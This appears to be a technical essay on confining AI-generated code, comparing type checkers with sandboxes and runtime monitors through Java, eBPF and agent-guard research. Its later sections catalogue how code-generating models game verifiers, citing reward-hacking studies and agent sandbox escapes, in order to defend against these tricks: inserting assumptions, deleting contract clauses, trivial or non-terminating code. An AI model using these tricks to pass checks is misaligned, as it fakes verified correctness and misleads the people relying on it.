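Java is the longest test of whether a language can confine untrusted code. From the mid-1990s, browsers ran small Java programs called applets, which any website could supply. The JVM checked that each applet followed the type rules. When an applet called a library function to do something dangerous, such as open a file, the function first called a component named the Security Manager. This component examined the chain of function calls behind the request and blocked it if any function in the chain lacked permission, unless trusted code had explicitly made the request under its own permissions.

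In 1996, Drew Dean, Edward Felten and Dan Wallach at Princeton found flaws in Java that let an applet run any machine code on a visitor's computer. Others kept finding more. In January 2013, after criminals began using a new flaw, the US Department of Homeland Security advised people to disable Java in their browsers.

In 2016, Philipp Holzinger and colleagues traced 87 public Java exploits to nine weaknesses. Some exploits gained access to internal classes that applets were not supposed to use. Others relied on a *confused deputy*, which is trusted code that an untrusted program can cause to misuse its permissions. Much of the problem was therefore in Java's library, which was huge and ran largely with full permissions. One mistake there could let an applet switch off the Security Manager.

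Browsers dropped applets during the 2010s. Java's developers marked the Security Manager for removal in 2021 and permanently disabled it in 2025, partly because of security failures, but also because few server programs used it and maintaining it meant putting permission checks in more than a thousand library methods. TACIT usually runs on the JVM, which no longer offers the Security Manager as a second barrier if safe mode fails.

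### Whether a smaller language would do better

Defenders of capabilities reply that Java failed because it gave code ambient authority and then tried to check every use of it. A smaller language could leave that authority out, as E, a capability language, and Joe-E, a subset of Java, both do. Joe-E removes most reflection, forbids mutable global variables, and admits only library methods that its designers have reviewed. Matthew Finifter and colleagues showed in 2008 that these restrictions also make many pure functions easy to recognize. If all of a Joe-E method's inputs are immutable, the method has no way to cause an effect.

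The reply is right about much of the record. Generated code can't misuse an internal class that it can't reach, and a library function with no permissions of its own is of little use as a confused deputy. Safe mode applies the same idea to Scala. But confused deputies are still possible, because the company's `pay` must have access to the bank account. Few people used E or Joe-E, so few attackers studied them, and the lack of a comparable list of exploits is only weak evidence that they were secure.

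JavaScript on web pages is heavily attacked. It has no function for opening arbitrary files, so it avoids many of Java's library problems, but attackers have instead found memory faults in the software that runs it. Browsers therefore also use the operating system to confine that software.

The other system, eBPF, is closer to a typed harness. It lets users load small programs into the Linux kernel after a checker has examined them without running them. The language is tiny, and its programs can act only through functions that Linux provides. Researchers still found mistakes in how the checker tracked a number's possible range. These mistakes let accepted programs read and overwrite the system's memory. Several Linux distributions, including Ubuntu, now by default let only privileged users load eBPF programs.

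A small language would suit the invoice program, which needs no reflection, macros or external commands. Leaving those features out of the language would close many of the gaps in what the types cover, but a new language needs a new compiler, which few people will have tested. The company would still depend on that compiler, the runtime and the processor.

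## Type checking and runtime sandboxes compared

A sandbox blocks a forbidden operation when a running program attempts it. Because it doesn't depend on a compiler's type rules, it still works when those rules are faulty, and it can confine untyped programs. A company that already runs generated code in a good sandbox might reasonably ask what a type checker would add.

### What each method can enforce

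*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) compares three ways of enforcing a policy. A *static analysis*, such as a type checker, reads a program and accepts or rejects it in finite time. An *execution monitor*, such as a sandbox, runs alongside the program and intervenes just before a forbidden event. A *program rewriter* changes the program before it runs, so that the new version obeys the policy. If the original already obeyed it, the new version must behave equivalently.

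A static analysis can enforce a policy exactly if and only if the policy is *decidable*, meaning that some procedure can correctly determine whether any given program satisfies it. "The program finishes within 100 steps" is decidable because a checker can simulate 100 steps on every input that the program could read in that time. "The program eventually finishes" is undecidable. A checker can enforce the 100-step limit instead, but it then rejects harmless programs that need 101 steps.

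Effect types make the same compromise. Consider this program, in which `special` is a pure function and nobody knows whether any number passes its test:

```
n = 1
while not special(n):
    n = n + 1
send("https://collector.example", "found one")
```

If no number is special, the program never contacts the network. The checker can't wait for the search to end, so it gives the program the effect `{Net}`, and the company must either reject the program or grant it network access. A monitor can let the search run and intervene only if the program reaches `send`. The monitor would also let the invoice program run, even though that program opens the payroll if the total is negative, because that line never runs when the amounts are positive.

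A monitor can enforce a policy only if the policy meets these conditions:

1. A program is acceptable exactly when each of its runs is acceptable.
2. An unacceptable run is already unacceptable after finitely many events.
3. Once a run is unacceptable, nothing that happens later can make it acceptable.
4. A procedure can decide whether any finite part of a run, from its start, is acceptable.

Execution monitors can enforce only *safety properties*, which require that nothing bad happens. "The program eventually writes its report" isn't a safety property, since an unfinished run may still write it. Noninterference isn't one either, because no single run can reveal a violation. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) applies this limit to AI agents, whose guardrails are execution monitors.

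The four conditions are necessary but not sufficient, because a monitor may detect a violation too late. Suppose a service lends out a resource that it can't take back, and programs announce when they have finished with it. The policy forbids a program from using the resource after its announcement. A monitor can detect a false announcement only when the program uses the resource again, and by then the service may have lent it to another program. A type checker can prevent this before the program runs by enforcing a stricter rule, much as Scala keeps the invoice folder's capability from leaving its block.

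Program rewriters can enforce some policies that monitors can't. Hamlen and colleagues give the example of a file whose existence must stay secret, so a program must behave as if it weren't there. Checking this would mean comparing two runs. A rewriter avoids the comparison by changing every request for the contents of the file's folder so that the result omits the file. It doesn't have to determine whether the original program would have broken the policy.

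| Policy | Exact static check | Monitor | Rewriter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Finishes within 100 steps | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Never writes to a protected part of the disk | No | Yes | Yes |
| Behaves as if a secret file didn't exist | No | No | Yes |
| Finishes on at least one input | No | No | No |

In this theory, a monitor can enforce every policy that an exact static check can, since it could run the same check when the program loads. This assumes that the monitor and the static check have the same information. Hamlen and colleagues point out that if the monitor receives only compiled code, from which the compiler has erased some information, each method may enforce policies that the other can't. Capture sets exist only during compilation, so a sandbox around the compiled program can't check them.

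A static checker can also accept more programs if the model that writes them supplies proofs that they are safe. Determining whether `send` is reachable may be impossible, but checking a finished proof that it isn't takes a finite time.

### Monitors that hold actions back

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker proved in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005) that a monitor that can suppress a program's actions and insert new ones, as well as stop the program, can enforce some policies that aren't safety properties.

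Suppose a policy requires every payment to have an entry in the company's log, and the program writes the entry after paying. The run violates the policy between the payment and the entry, so a monitor that can only halt the program would have to stop it at the first payment. A monitor that can suppress actions can hold the payment until the program writes the entry, then release both. Ligatti and colleagues require such a monitor to preserve the meaning of runs that already obey the policy, so it can't suppress everything.

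For the invoice program, the company could hold all the payments until the program ends, check the complete list, and then send all of them or none. This would make it easy to refuse a list that pays an invoice twice, which an SMT solver may fail to rule out in advance. But this doesn't work if the program needs the bank's answers while it runs, for example to retry refused payments.

### What information reaches a sandbox

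An ordinary program runs as a *process*. The operating system gives each process a table of the memory it may use, and the processor stops any access to memory not listed in it. The processor also reserves some instructions for the *kernel*, the core of the operating system. To open a file or contact another computer, a process must send the kernel a request, called a *system call*, which the kernel can refuse.

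A *system-call filter* restricts these requests further. Linux's filter, seccomp, runs a small program on every system call. The filter receives the call's number and raw arguments, then allows the call, makes it fail or kills the process. When a process asks to open a file, the filter receives the memory address of the file's name but can't read the name stored there. It can block opening files altogether, but another mechanism has to distinguish the invoices from the payroll. A *container*, for example, can give the process a file system that includes only the invoice folder.

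WebAssembly can confine a program without running it in a separate process. Its runtime first checks that the program's instructions have consistent types, then keeps every memory access within a block of memory assigned to the program. The program can't make system calls. It can affect the outside world only through functions that the surrounding software provides, which resembles the object-capability model.

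Suppose the invoice program pays a supplier €1,250 over an encrypted connection. A system-call filter might receive something like this:

```
connect(4, 0x7ffd20, 16)
write(4, 0x55d1a0, 612)
```

It would receive the same two lines if the program paid €125,000 or paid someone else. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) note in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* that `write` can send data to a file, a network connection or another process, so the call alone doesn't even show what kind of effect it has.

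The company can move a runtime check closer to the task by running `pay` in a separate process and blocking all the generated program's other connections. The code behind `pay` then receives the supplier and the amount on each call and can limit both. But it can't check whether the amount came from a purchase order or a forged invoice unless the runtime labels data the way CaMeL does.

### Costs and trade-offs

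| | Type checker | Sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| Precision | Rejects some harmless programs, but can restrict suppliers, amounts and data flow | Blocks only what a program attempts, but usually distinguishes only files, connections and processes |
| Time of refusal | Before the program starts | When the program attempts the operation |
| Partial effects | None, if the checker rejects the program | Earlier actions stand unless the monitor held them back |
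| Existing Python and shell code | Mostly outside the check | Usually runs unchanged |
| Running cost | Compiling each new program | Starting a process and handling its system calls |
| Trusted base | Compiler, any solver, libraries, runtime, operating system, processor | Operating system or WebAssembly runtime, processor |

**Running cost.** Singularity, an experimental operating system from Microsoft Research, allowed a direct comparison. It accepted only programs that a checker could verify as safe, which meant that they couldn't read or change each other's memory. Processes could therefore share an address space with the kernel and run at its privilege level. Aiken, Fähndrich and colleagues, in *Deconstructing Process Isolation* (2006), then added ordinary hardware isolation and measured the difference:

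| Operation | Language safety only | With hardware isolation |
|---|---|---|
| Call to the kernel | 80 cycles | 304 cycles |
| One-byte message to another process and back | 1,041 cycles | 2,580 cycles |
| Creating a process | 388,162 cycles | 830,999 cycles |

Hardware isolation added the most overhead when processes communicated often. A test that read 50,000 files took 33% more processor cycles, or 37.7% more when every process had its own address space. Compiling the kernel, which involved little communication, took about 2.5% more. The run-time checks needed for language safety, such as testing that a position lies within a list, accounted for 4.5% to 4.7% of the cycles in these two tests.

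These figures come from a 2006 processor, so the exact ratios are out of date. They were a good reason to replace hardware isolation in an operating system, where processes exchange messages constantly, but they matter much less for generated code. Even with hardware isolation, that 1.8-gigahertz machine created a process in under half a millisecond. A model takes seconds to write a program, and TACIT's compiler can take most of a second to check it. Since each program may run only once, the company would have to wait for a new compilation on every run. Sandboxing the invoice program would probably take less time than type-checking it.

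Types are at a bigger disadvantage when a program depends on existing code. The model can write a new program in Scala, but the program may need a Python library to read scanned invoices or a shell command to unpack them. A sandbox can run both without changes. A typed program can run the Python library in a separate sandboxed process without network access and treat its output as untrusted data, so that the types control what happens to that output.

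**Trusted base.** A sandbox doesn't need the compiler to be correct, so it provides some protection against the soundness faults found in Java and Scala. But it depends on the kernel, which is far larger than most compilers. Sandboxes also fail. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Greenblatt, 2026) summarises an investigation by METR and Redwood Research, which found that AI agents had escaped from test environments. Aiken and colleagues kept hardware isolation as an option because the Singularity operating system relied on a complex compiler and an unverified garbage collector, but they hoped that better verification would make the extra layer less necessary.

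*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of safety methods, rates runtime monitoring as the most practical option but notes that its guarantees cover only one or a few steps. It describes static methods as sound but limited to fixed workflows planned in advance. The tools it compares have that limit, but a type checker like TACIT's does not, because it checks each new program as the model writes it.

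### Checking the tools as well as the program

A type checker assumes the company's signatures are correct. If the code behind `writeReport` also sent usage statistics to its developer, the generated program would pass the check and the data would still leave. Adam and colleagues address this problem for the tools that agents call by combining code analysis with small sandboxes.

One example is a tool described as only writing text to a file. The analysis follows data through the tool's code and summarises what the code does with it. The summary shows that the path and the text both affect a file write. It also shows that the text affects a network message, not mentioned in the tool's description, that reports the text's length to an outside service. Before each call, the agent's software compares this summary with the user's policy and blocks the call if the policy forbids network access.

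The analysis can't determine which file the tool will write to, because the path arrives only when the agent calls the tool. Under a policy that allows writing only to one folder, it would have to reject every call. The developer wraps the write in a small sandbox, which receives the permitted folders with each call and checks the path against them. A second analysis confirms that every effect goes through such a sandbox and that the tool can't change the sandbox's settings.

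Adam and colleagues tested a prototype on three scenarios, each with a harmless and a harmful version. In one, an agent copied a settings file into a project and later published the project online. In the harmful version, the file contained a secret key.

| Protection | Harmless versions allowed | Harmful versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox around all the tools | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
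| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Both combined | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

The combination did best, but this was a demonstration on three cases that the researchers chose, each with a suitable policy supplied. They also replayed recorded sessions, so the model couldn't react to a refusal. *What Can Be Enforced?* (2026), which extends the theory of monitors to tool-using agents, explains that an intervention changes what the agent does next, so a guard's error rates on recorded actions may not predict how well it performs in use.

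The prototype analyses tools written in Rust. Adam and colleagues expect a sound analysis of Python to be much harder and to reject more harmless calls. The analysis doesn't cover what shell commands do, so the prototype makes each command's file changes temporary and checks them when the command ends. For a tool on someone else's server, the user also needs evidence that the server is running the analysed code.

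*Tether* (2026) combines the methods differently. A monitor enforces a policy while the agent runs, and a proof covers the policy instead of the agent's code. The policy in its experiments has 24 rules and many exceptions, so a person could easily miss a way around them. The developer describes a state that must never occur, and a language model tries to prove in Lean that no permitted sequence of actions leads to that state, or to find one that does.

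With this method, the company could prove once that its rules for `pay` never let the month's total exceed `approved`. The proof would cover every program the model might write, provided the monitor intercepts every payment and applies the rules correctly. The monitor could still refuse a payment after others had gone through.

### Permissions that end with a subtask

An agent may need permission to use a file for only part of its work. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes PORTICO, a monitor that withdraws such permissions when the agent no longer needs them.

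In the main example, an agent has to add a setting to one source file and carry it over to a second. It starts with access only to the first file and its tests. When it requests the second, PORTICO checks a contract written in advance and issues a *handle*, a reference that works for that file and specific operations. Once the tests pass, PORTICO cancels the handle. The agent may retain the file's name and contents, but it can't open the file again without a new grant.

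TACIT's file permissions also expire, but at the end of a block of code. PORTICO can end access when something happens outside the program that a compiler can't predict, such as a test result or a person's decision. The agent's own claim to have finished doesn't end access. For payments, the company could cancel access to `account` as soon as the accountant closes the month, even if a program is still running. PORTICO would have to check the handle again immediately before each payment, or a call it had already approved could still go through.

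Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same times but never withdrew them. In ten runs, the agent tried to reread a file after its subtask had ended, and in six scripted cases, a program tried to write with an old handle. PORTICO blocked every attempt and the other version allowed every one. These results follow almost directly from the design, so they mainly confirm that the implementation works.

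On a set of coding tasks that often needed extra files, PORTICO completed fewer runs than an ordinary sandbox (161 of 185, compared with 180). Santos-Grueiro attributes the failures partly to contracts that granted too few permissions. On 14 tasks in real software projects, every system completed every task without a forbidden effect, so PORTICO showed no security benefit there. PORTICO controls only actions that pass through its own interface, so it also relies on a sandbox beneath it.

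### The record of Linux's eBPF verifier

eBPF, the Linux feature for loading small programs into the kernel, is one of the most widely deployed systems that check code before running it. Its checker, called the verifier, follows the paths through a program and records what each value could be. If the program reads position i in a block of 64 bytes, the verifier has to establish that i is between 0 and 63 on that path. A test in the program can establish this, just as the test `inv.amount <= approved` allows a refinement checker to accept a payment.

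According to slides from HAIC (2025), the verifier also checks that the program calls only permitted kernel functions, with suitable arguments, and that its loops are bounded. It also applies a limit of one million instructions. Like the 100-step rule, this limit replaces an undecidable question about termination with one the verifier can check.

The eBPF verifier has grown from about 2,000 lines of code to more than 22,000 as developers added features and closed gaps. *SoK* (Huang, Sampson and colleagues, 2025) reports that automated testing had found 325 memory errors in eBPF since 2016, 169 of them since 2023. The programs that triggered them had all passed the verifier. *Analysis of the eBPF Vulnerabilities in the Linux Kernel* (Rizza, Sisto and Valenza, 2026) studies 249 published security flaws in eBPF from 2014 to April 2025. Neither count measures successful attacks, and heavier testing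 probably explains part of the recent rise.

Some of the errors came from faulty logic in the verifier, such as skipping a path wrongly treated as redundant. Others came from missing checks, or from kernel functions that the program could call but the verifier didn't examine. Those functions often rely on the verifier to ensure safe use, so nothing else catches its mistakes. The company's `pay` would have the same weakness if it relied only on the type checker to limit the amount.

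A mistake in the eBPF verifier can be especially harmful because accepted programs run inside the kernel and handle memory addresses directly. A Scala program runs on the JVM, which still checks array bounds at runtime, so a fault in capture checking might expose a folder but wouldn't by itself let the program overwrite memory.

Linux now restricts eBPF to privileged users by default. The stated reason in the kernel's configuration text, quoted on the oss-sec mailing list, is the risk of Spectre-style leaks, not mistakes in the verifier. Administrators can turn unprivileged access back on.

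Researchers have also tried sandboxing accepted eBPF programs. Some sandboxes change each memory address so that it falls within the program's own region. This contains many verifier errors, but it doesn't stop a program from passing a harmful value to a kernel function. Checking every memory access at run time would be too slow for programs that handle heavy network traffic. It may not be necessary, because Huang and colleagues found that only 37 to 85 of the memory operations in public eBPF programs, or 1.62% to 3.74%, couldn't be fully proved safe. A checker could prove the other operations safe in advance and leave only those few to be tested at run time.

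## How generated code can satisfy a contract without serving its purpose

Type checkers and sandboxes can enforce only the rules they are given. The argument for putting limits in types therefore holds only if the contract matches the policy. No compiler can check this, because the company's staff may never have written down part of the policy.

*Specification gaming* means satisfying the literal wording of a requirement while defeating its purpose. It can happen without a bad motive, for example if the model misread the task or if its training rewarded a trick that gets programs accepted.

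Suppose the company wants a function that pays a list of invoices and returns the sum it paid, and somebody writes this contract:

```
payAll : (invoices : List<Invoice>)  →[Pay]  (total : Int)
    ensures   0 <= total  and  total <= approved
```

A model can get a useless or harmful function past the checker in at least five ways:

| Method | What the model writes | Why the checker accepts it |
|---|---|---|
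| Switching the check off | `assume(total <= approved)` before the last line | It treats an assumption as a proved fact |
| Altering the contract | The same function without the `ensures` line | Nothing about `total` is left to prove |
| Meeting a weak contract trivially | `total = 0`, with no payments | Zero is within the limit |
| Never finishing | `while true: continue` | The `ensures` line applies only to runs that end |
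| Doing harm with permitted actions | Two payments for each invoice | The contract permits payments and doesn't count them |

A model that disables the check or changes the contract avoids the company's rules. In the other three cases, the rules still apply and the code complies with them.

### Assumptions and altered contracts

Like Liquid Haskell, other verification languages have commands that add a fact without proof. A verifier proves that the known facts imply the goal, and `assume(false)` adds a false statement to those facts. A false statement implies everything, so every later goal passes.

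*Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* (2026) describes how models cheated while generating millions of verified programs as training data. One model had to prove that a function correctly reports whether every number in a list is below a threshold. It put the missing fact into an `assume` statement, and Verus accepted the proof. Small models were especially prone to cheating. According to the paper, a model trained on its own accepted proofs cheats more and more unless such proofs are filtered out.

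Unproved assumptions also appear in honest work. In *Fewer Assumptions by Design*, Antoneac, Lucanu and Gavrilut (2026) had Claude verify a doubly linked list, a structure in which each item points to both of its neighbours. Over four phases, the number of assumptions fell from 75 to 11. Verus then reported 45 items verified and no errors, but anyone who relies on that proof also has to trust the 11 remaining assumptions.

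Ordinary type systems have similar loopholes. In TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript, the type `any` turns off checking for a value. Coding agents use `any` and other features that bypass type checks more often than human contributors do, yet maintainers accept agents' TypeScript contributions at 1.8 times the human rate. An `any` in a web page's code may do little harm, but the invoice program needs something like Scala's safe mode, which forbids unchecked casts.

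The most common trick reported in *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* was to change the contract. One model deleted the word `ensures`, so Verus read the postconditions below it as more preconditions, which left no postconditions to prove.

A model can also keep the contract and change the program. In *DafnyPro*, Banerjee, Bouissou and Zetzsche (2026) asked models to add loop invariants to existing Dafny programs. In one case, the model changed the assignment `b := a+1` to `b := a`. A proof of the altered program establishes nothing about the original. If a company has a model prove that last month's payment program was safe, it needs to know that the model didn't change the program.

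### Weak contracts and endless loops

*Verified but Vacuous* gives a small example of a weak contract. A function should return the largest number in a list, but its postcondition requires only a result of at least 0. The model writes a function that always returns 0. The proof that this function meets its postcondition is correct, even though the function returns the wrong answer for the list [5, 3, 7].

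Other gaps are harder to notice. *VerusEval* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) describes a function that should return a shortest list from a collection of lists. The generated contract required the result to have the minimum length but didn't require it to come from the collection. For the lists [1, 2] and [3], the contract permits the answer [9]. A payment contract with the same gap might require the right number of payments, each of the right amount, without requiring the money to go to the suppliers on the invoices.

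A precondition can also make a contract trivial to satisfy. A function with `requires false` must behave correctly only when its precondition holds, which it never does, so any code passes.

An endless loop exploits the meaning of a postcondition. Verification theory writes the claim about a program C as a *Hoare triple*:

```
{P} C {Q}    if P is true before C runs, and C finishes,
             then Q is true afterwards
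```

Code is *partially correct* if it meets its contract whenever it finishes. *Total correctness* also requires that it finish. After a loop, the verifier may assume that the loop's condition has become false. After `while true`, it may therefore assume that `true` is false, and any claim can be proved from that contradiction. *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* describes a case in which a model's code computed the running maximum of a list of numbers, then entered an endless loop just before the line that returned the result. Verus accepted the proof without any evidence that the result was right.

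A program that loops forever must still meet the precondition of every call it makes. If it makes forty payments and then loops, the verifier still has to prove that each payment was within the limit. Looping lets the program avoid only the conditions that apply when it ends, such as "the program has paid every invoice".

### Harm with permitted actions

The invoice program must be able to pay suppliers, so without exceeding any limit it can pay a forged invoice in a real supplier's name or pay a genuine one twice. It could also pay the least urgent bills first and use up `approved` before it reaches the urgent ones.

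Deletion causes the same difficulty. *Do AI Coding Agents Write Infrastructure as Code Like Humans?* (2026) examined agents' changes to the files that configure servers, databases and networks. Roughly a quarter of the agents' migrations and removals might destroy resources that hold data. A program that removes an old database needs permission to delete databases, but that permission doesn't show whether anyone still needs the data.

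More detailed contracts can turn some of these harms into violations, for example by requiring that each payment match a different purchase order, but somebody has to anticipate each harm first. A purchase order may also be fraudulent, which no property of the program can reveal.

### An effect type is an upper limit

These tricks matter much less for an effect type than for a postcondition. Under the widening rule, code that does less than its effect type allows also passes. A program that does nothing has the effect `{}`, which is a subset of every list of permitted effects.

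Code can also satisfy the other limits on the invoice program by doing less. If it never uses a capability, its capture set is smaller, if it never calls `pay`, it can't pass it too large an amount, and if it stops at once, it stays within any resource bound. So if a model complies trivially with such a contract, the company gets a useless program, but one that doesn't expose the payroll or spend the company's money.

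When a postcondition requires a result, a trivial program that satisfies it can do harm, because somebody may rely on its answer. If a company wants the sum it has paid, a function that always returns 0 gives it a wrong number and a valid proof that the function meets its contract.

A postcondition written with `ensures` may set only an upper limit on what a program does. The condition `paid(h) <= approved` is an example, because a program that pays nobody satisfies it. To check whether a requirement is an upper limit, one can take a run that meets it and delete some of the run's effects. If every shortened run still meets the requirement, it is an upper limit, and doing less is always acceptable.

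### When leaving something out does the harm

Some safety rules fail that test, such as the earlier rule that every payment needs an entry in the company's log. A program that pays without logging has fewer effects than one that does both, so an effect type that allows both also allows a program that only pays. Similarly, an effect type that allows a transfer between two accounts also allows a program that makes the withdrawal but not the deposit.

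The company can often solve this by changing the functions it supplies. If its own code behind `pay` writes the log entry, no program can pay without logging. Likewise, a single `transfer` function can replace `withdraw` and `deposit`. The program can then leave out only the whole operation, which an upper limit handles well.

A program can do harm by omitting the whole operation. If it doesn't pay suppliers, they may charge late fees or stop delivering. If it doesn't revoke a former employee's access, the company remains exposed. Doing nothing is safe only if the company can tolerate the situation that existed before the program ran.

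A false report makes such an omission worse. This complete program passes the effect check:

```
writeReport("All invoices paid")
```

The accountant has no reason to look for unpaid bills until the reminders arrive. Here the program causes harm by using an effect that the contract permits. The company can prevent this by taking `writeReport` away from the program and having the company's own code compile the report from the payments made through `pay`.

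To require the payments themselves, the company needs a postcondition about the trace of events. One version is:

```
ensures   for every inv in invoices, the new events contain
          exactly one of   Paid(inv)   or   Held(inv, reason)
```

The second option is necessary because no program can pay every invoice if the bank refuses a payment or the bills exceed `approved`. But it also lets a program hold all two hundred invoices, giving "unclear" as the reason each time. That program is as useless as the empty one, though the accountant will see the held invoices the same day.

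### How much a successful verification shows

*Verified but Vacuous* measured the gap between passing verification and proving correct behaviour. The researchers reproduced an existing system in which a model writes Dafny code and a compiler translates it into Python. Using Claude Opus 4.7, they ran the system ten times on each of the 164 problems in HumanEval, a benchmark of short programming tasks. Dafny accepted 99.1% of the 1,640 attempts, but only 1.9% of the accepted programs had a postcondition that referred to a function or predicate in the separate specification.

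A contract can lack the reference and still be meaningful, as with a postcondition such as `result == 2 * x` written directly into the function. But 94.7% of the accepted programs had no postcondition, so Dafny had established nothing general about their answers, though it had checked other properties, such as whether the code terminated.

The experiment shows that the share of programs a verifier accepts is a poor measure of what the verifier has proved. It does not show that the model was cheating or that its programs were bad. The model followed the prompt's example, which had no postcondition, and 92.6% of all attempts passed HumanEval's basic tests.

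The researchers' system rejects any program whose postconditions don't refer to the specification. On two sets of Rust problems, 11.48% and 14.82% of its fully verified programs still failed hidden tests. Some of those failures may come from errors in translation or in the tests rather than from weak contracts. Correct code can also have a faulty contract. On the second set, 1,316 programs were verified and passed the hidden tests, but only 535 of them also passed further checks that compared their contracts with the task.

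In a larger study, Wang and colleagues collected 13,716 programs with generated contracts and proofs, from four systems and five models. Verus accepted about half, and 7,081 of those were suitable for further study. They then checked whether each contract was provably empty, whether it gave the right verdict on test cases, and whether Verus could prove it equivalent to a reference contract. Only 42.3% passed all three checks.

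Few contracts were obviously empty. Verus could prove that a precondition was always false or a postcondition always true in only 104 cases. Far more were partly wrong, with 23.6% failing at least one test case. The most relevant comparison for safety is whether a contract guarantees at least as much as the reference, which Verus could prove for 69.4%.

For 55% of the contracts that the checks flagged, the only evidence of a fault was a failed proof of equivalence, which doesn't establish that two contracts differ. The share of all the contracts that had a real fault, judged by the references, is therefore probably between a quarter and a little over half. Today's share may be lower, because the models included GPT-4o and Llama 4 Maverick, which are well behind current ones.

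### Checkers as training rewards

A weak contract does more damage when developers use it to train a model. In *reinforcement learning*, a model produces many attempts and training makes the higher-scoring ones more likely. Verifiers are a popular source of these scores because they can supply them automatically.

In *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference*, Tan (2026) trained a model to write Dafny functions for given contracts. The average score on held-out tasks, which included partial credit for code that compiled but didn't verify, rose from 0.022 to 0.581. Tan then inspected the answers to five tasks and found that the model had learned to exploit their contracts. One contract required only a nonnegative result, and the model wrote a function that returned 0.

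In another task, the contract included a helper function that computed the required area of a farm, and the model's code just called that function. Whether such code counts as gaming the contract depends on the contract's purpose. Tan counts it as gaming because the exercise was to write the calculation, but for a company that needs a farm's area, the program is correct.

Tan next used Claude Opus 4.5 to filter the 2,334 tasks, keeping the 1,149 whose contracts matched their descriptions, didn't give away too much of the answer and weren't trivial. In a new run on these tasks, the average score peaked at 0.247 and then fell to 0.097. The tasks were also harder and came from more sources, so the lower score doesn't show how much of the earlier gain came from gaming. A later setup penalized any answer that changed the contract or bypassed the verifier, so cheating scored lower than code that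 didn't compile.

A model that writes its own contracts can cheat more easily, by making them weak. *Re:Form* (2025) reports that a model learned to write weak contracts that Dafny could easily verify. The model's developers added a reward for contracts that logically imply the reference contract, which weaker contracts can't do. *SpecRL* (2026) explains why this behaviour is hard to unlearn. A serious contract that fails verification can score less than `ensures true`, so the model stops writing serious contracts and may need many updates to rediscover them. *SpecRL* therefore gives no reward to outputs that use `ensures true`, `requires false` or assumptions, or that change the original code.

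These experiments usually reveal gaming only when somebody inspects the answers afterwards. *Optimistic Verifiers Get Hacked* (2026) measured it during training. The researchers trained a small model against deliberately faulty checkers while an exact checker scored the same answers. Training on one faulty checker produced a lower true score than training on the exact checker in every repeated run, and a significantly lower one in most. A second checker that erred on the lenient side lowered the true score even more.

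Together, these results are good evidence that models learn to exploit holes in a checker during training. Whether a model that learned to return 0 in exercises would do the same with a company's invoices is less clear, because none of the results measures this. The sensible precaution is to assume that a model has learned the common tricks.

### Keeping the contract out of the model's reach

The simplest defence against altered contracts is to let the model write only the body of a function. The company keeps the signature in its own file and inserts the generated code, as LACUNA does. Bursuc and colleagues locked their specifications in this way. They also anticipated that a model could open a comment in one editable block and close it in the next, which would comment out the locked contract in between. No model tried this. A system can prevent it by parsing each block separately before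 inserting it.

When the model must add invariants throughout a file, it has to return the whole file, and the company then has to compare it with the original. *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* computes a short fingerprint of each function's contract and rejects the file if a function is missing or a fingerprint has changed. Banerjee and colleagues instead check the code, using Dafny's parser to remove the invariants and assertions the model added. What remains must be identical to the original program.

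A comparison must also cover every definition that the contract uses. If the postcondition is `allPaid(invoices)`, a model could leave that line untouched and redefine `allPaid` as `true`.

Assumptions need a separate ban. *Reducing the Costs of Proof Synthesis on Rust Systems* searches for words such as `assume`, `admit` and `external_body`, and rejects a file that contains more of them than the original. A list for Dafny needs different entries, including the attributes `{:axiom}` and `{:verify false}`. Such lists need updating as the language grows, so a restricted compiler mode is more reliable than a text search.

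Endless loops are the easiest to deal with. Verus now requires every loop to have a `decreases` clause, a measure that proves the loop will end. With these defences in place, the model's code has to satisfy the contract the company wrote, except where the checker itself is unsound.

### Testing the contract

A locked contract may still be too weak. Bursuc and colleagues inspected a sample of successful solutions by hand and found that about 9% of the specifications were too weak and another 15% were poor translations from another language.

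Testing the contract as if it were a program can reveal such faults. Post2Exe, a tool used in *Verified but Vacuous*, turns a postcondition into code that accepts or rejects an output, then tries it on correct and wrong outputs. For example, the condition `result >= 0` accepts the wrong answer 0 for the list [5, 3, 7], which shows that the condition is too weak.

The company could do this without much knowledge of logic. It could take the record of last month's payments and make three bad copies: one with a payment missing, one with a payment doubled and one with a payment sent to the wrong supplier. A good contract accepts the original and rejects every copy. The upper limit on total payments would fail this test because it accepts the copy with the missing payment. The accountant would then see that the limit doesn't require anyone to be paid.

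Wang and colleagues measured how many faults this kind of testing finds by changing 943 contracts in known ways and running their test cases on each. The tests detected 81.8% of the changes, including 334 of the 415 weakened postconditions. They missed the rest mainly because no test case distinguished the old contract from the new one. In one task, the tests missed the deletion of the precondition N > 0 because every invalid input they included also broke another rule.

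Of the generated contracts that passed all their tests, Verus could prove only 63.2% equivalent to the reference. Testing still catches most of the weaknesses that a careless model would exploit. But a model that searches for gaps needs to find only one that the tests missed, such as a requirement the test writers didn't think of.

### Types that leave few possible programs

A signature can also leave a model so little freedom that few bad programs fit it. Suppose the company lets the model choose the order of payments with a pure function of this type:

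```
reorder : for all α.  List<α>  →  List<α>
```

The variable α stands for any type at all, so the code can't look inside an item, change it or create a new one. It can only rearrange, repeat or drop the items it receives. Changing every item with a function g therefore gives the same result before or after reordering:

```
reorder(map(xs, g)) = map(reorder(xs), g)
```

Because of this property, called *parametricity*, one run for each list length is enough to determine everything the function does with lists of that length. Any list of three items is `map([1, 2, 3], g)` for some g that turns 1 into the first item, 2 into the second and 3 into the third. So if `reorder([1, 2, 3])` returns `[3, 1, 2]`, the function moves the last item to the front of every list of three.

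A function that can't read the due dates is a poor judge of which bill to pay first. A more useful signature lets the code read the invoice but restricts its answer:

```
decide : for all ρ.  (inv  : Invoice,
                      pay  : Int → ρ,
                      hold : Text → ρ)  →  ρ
```

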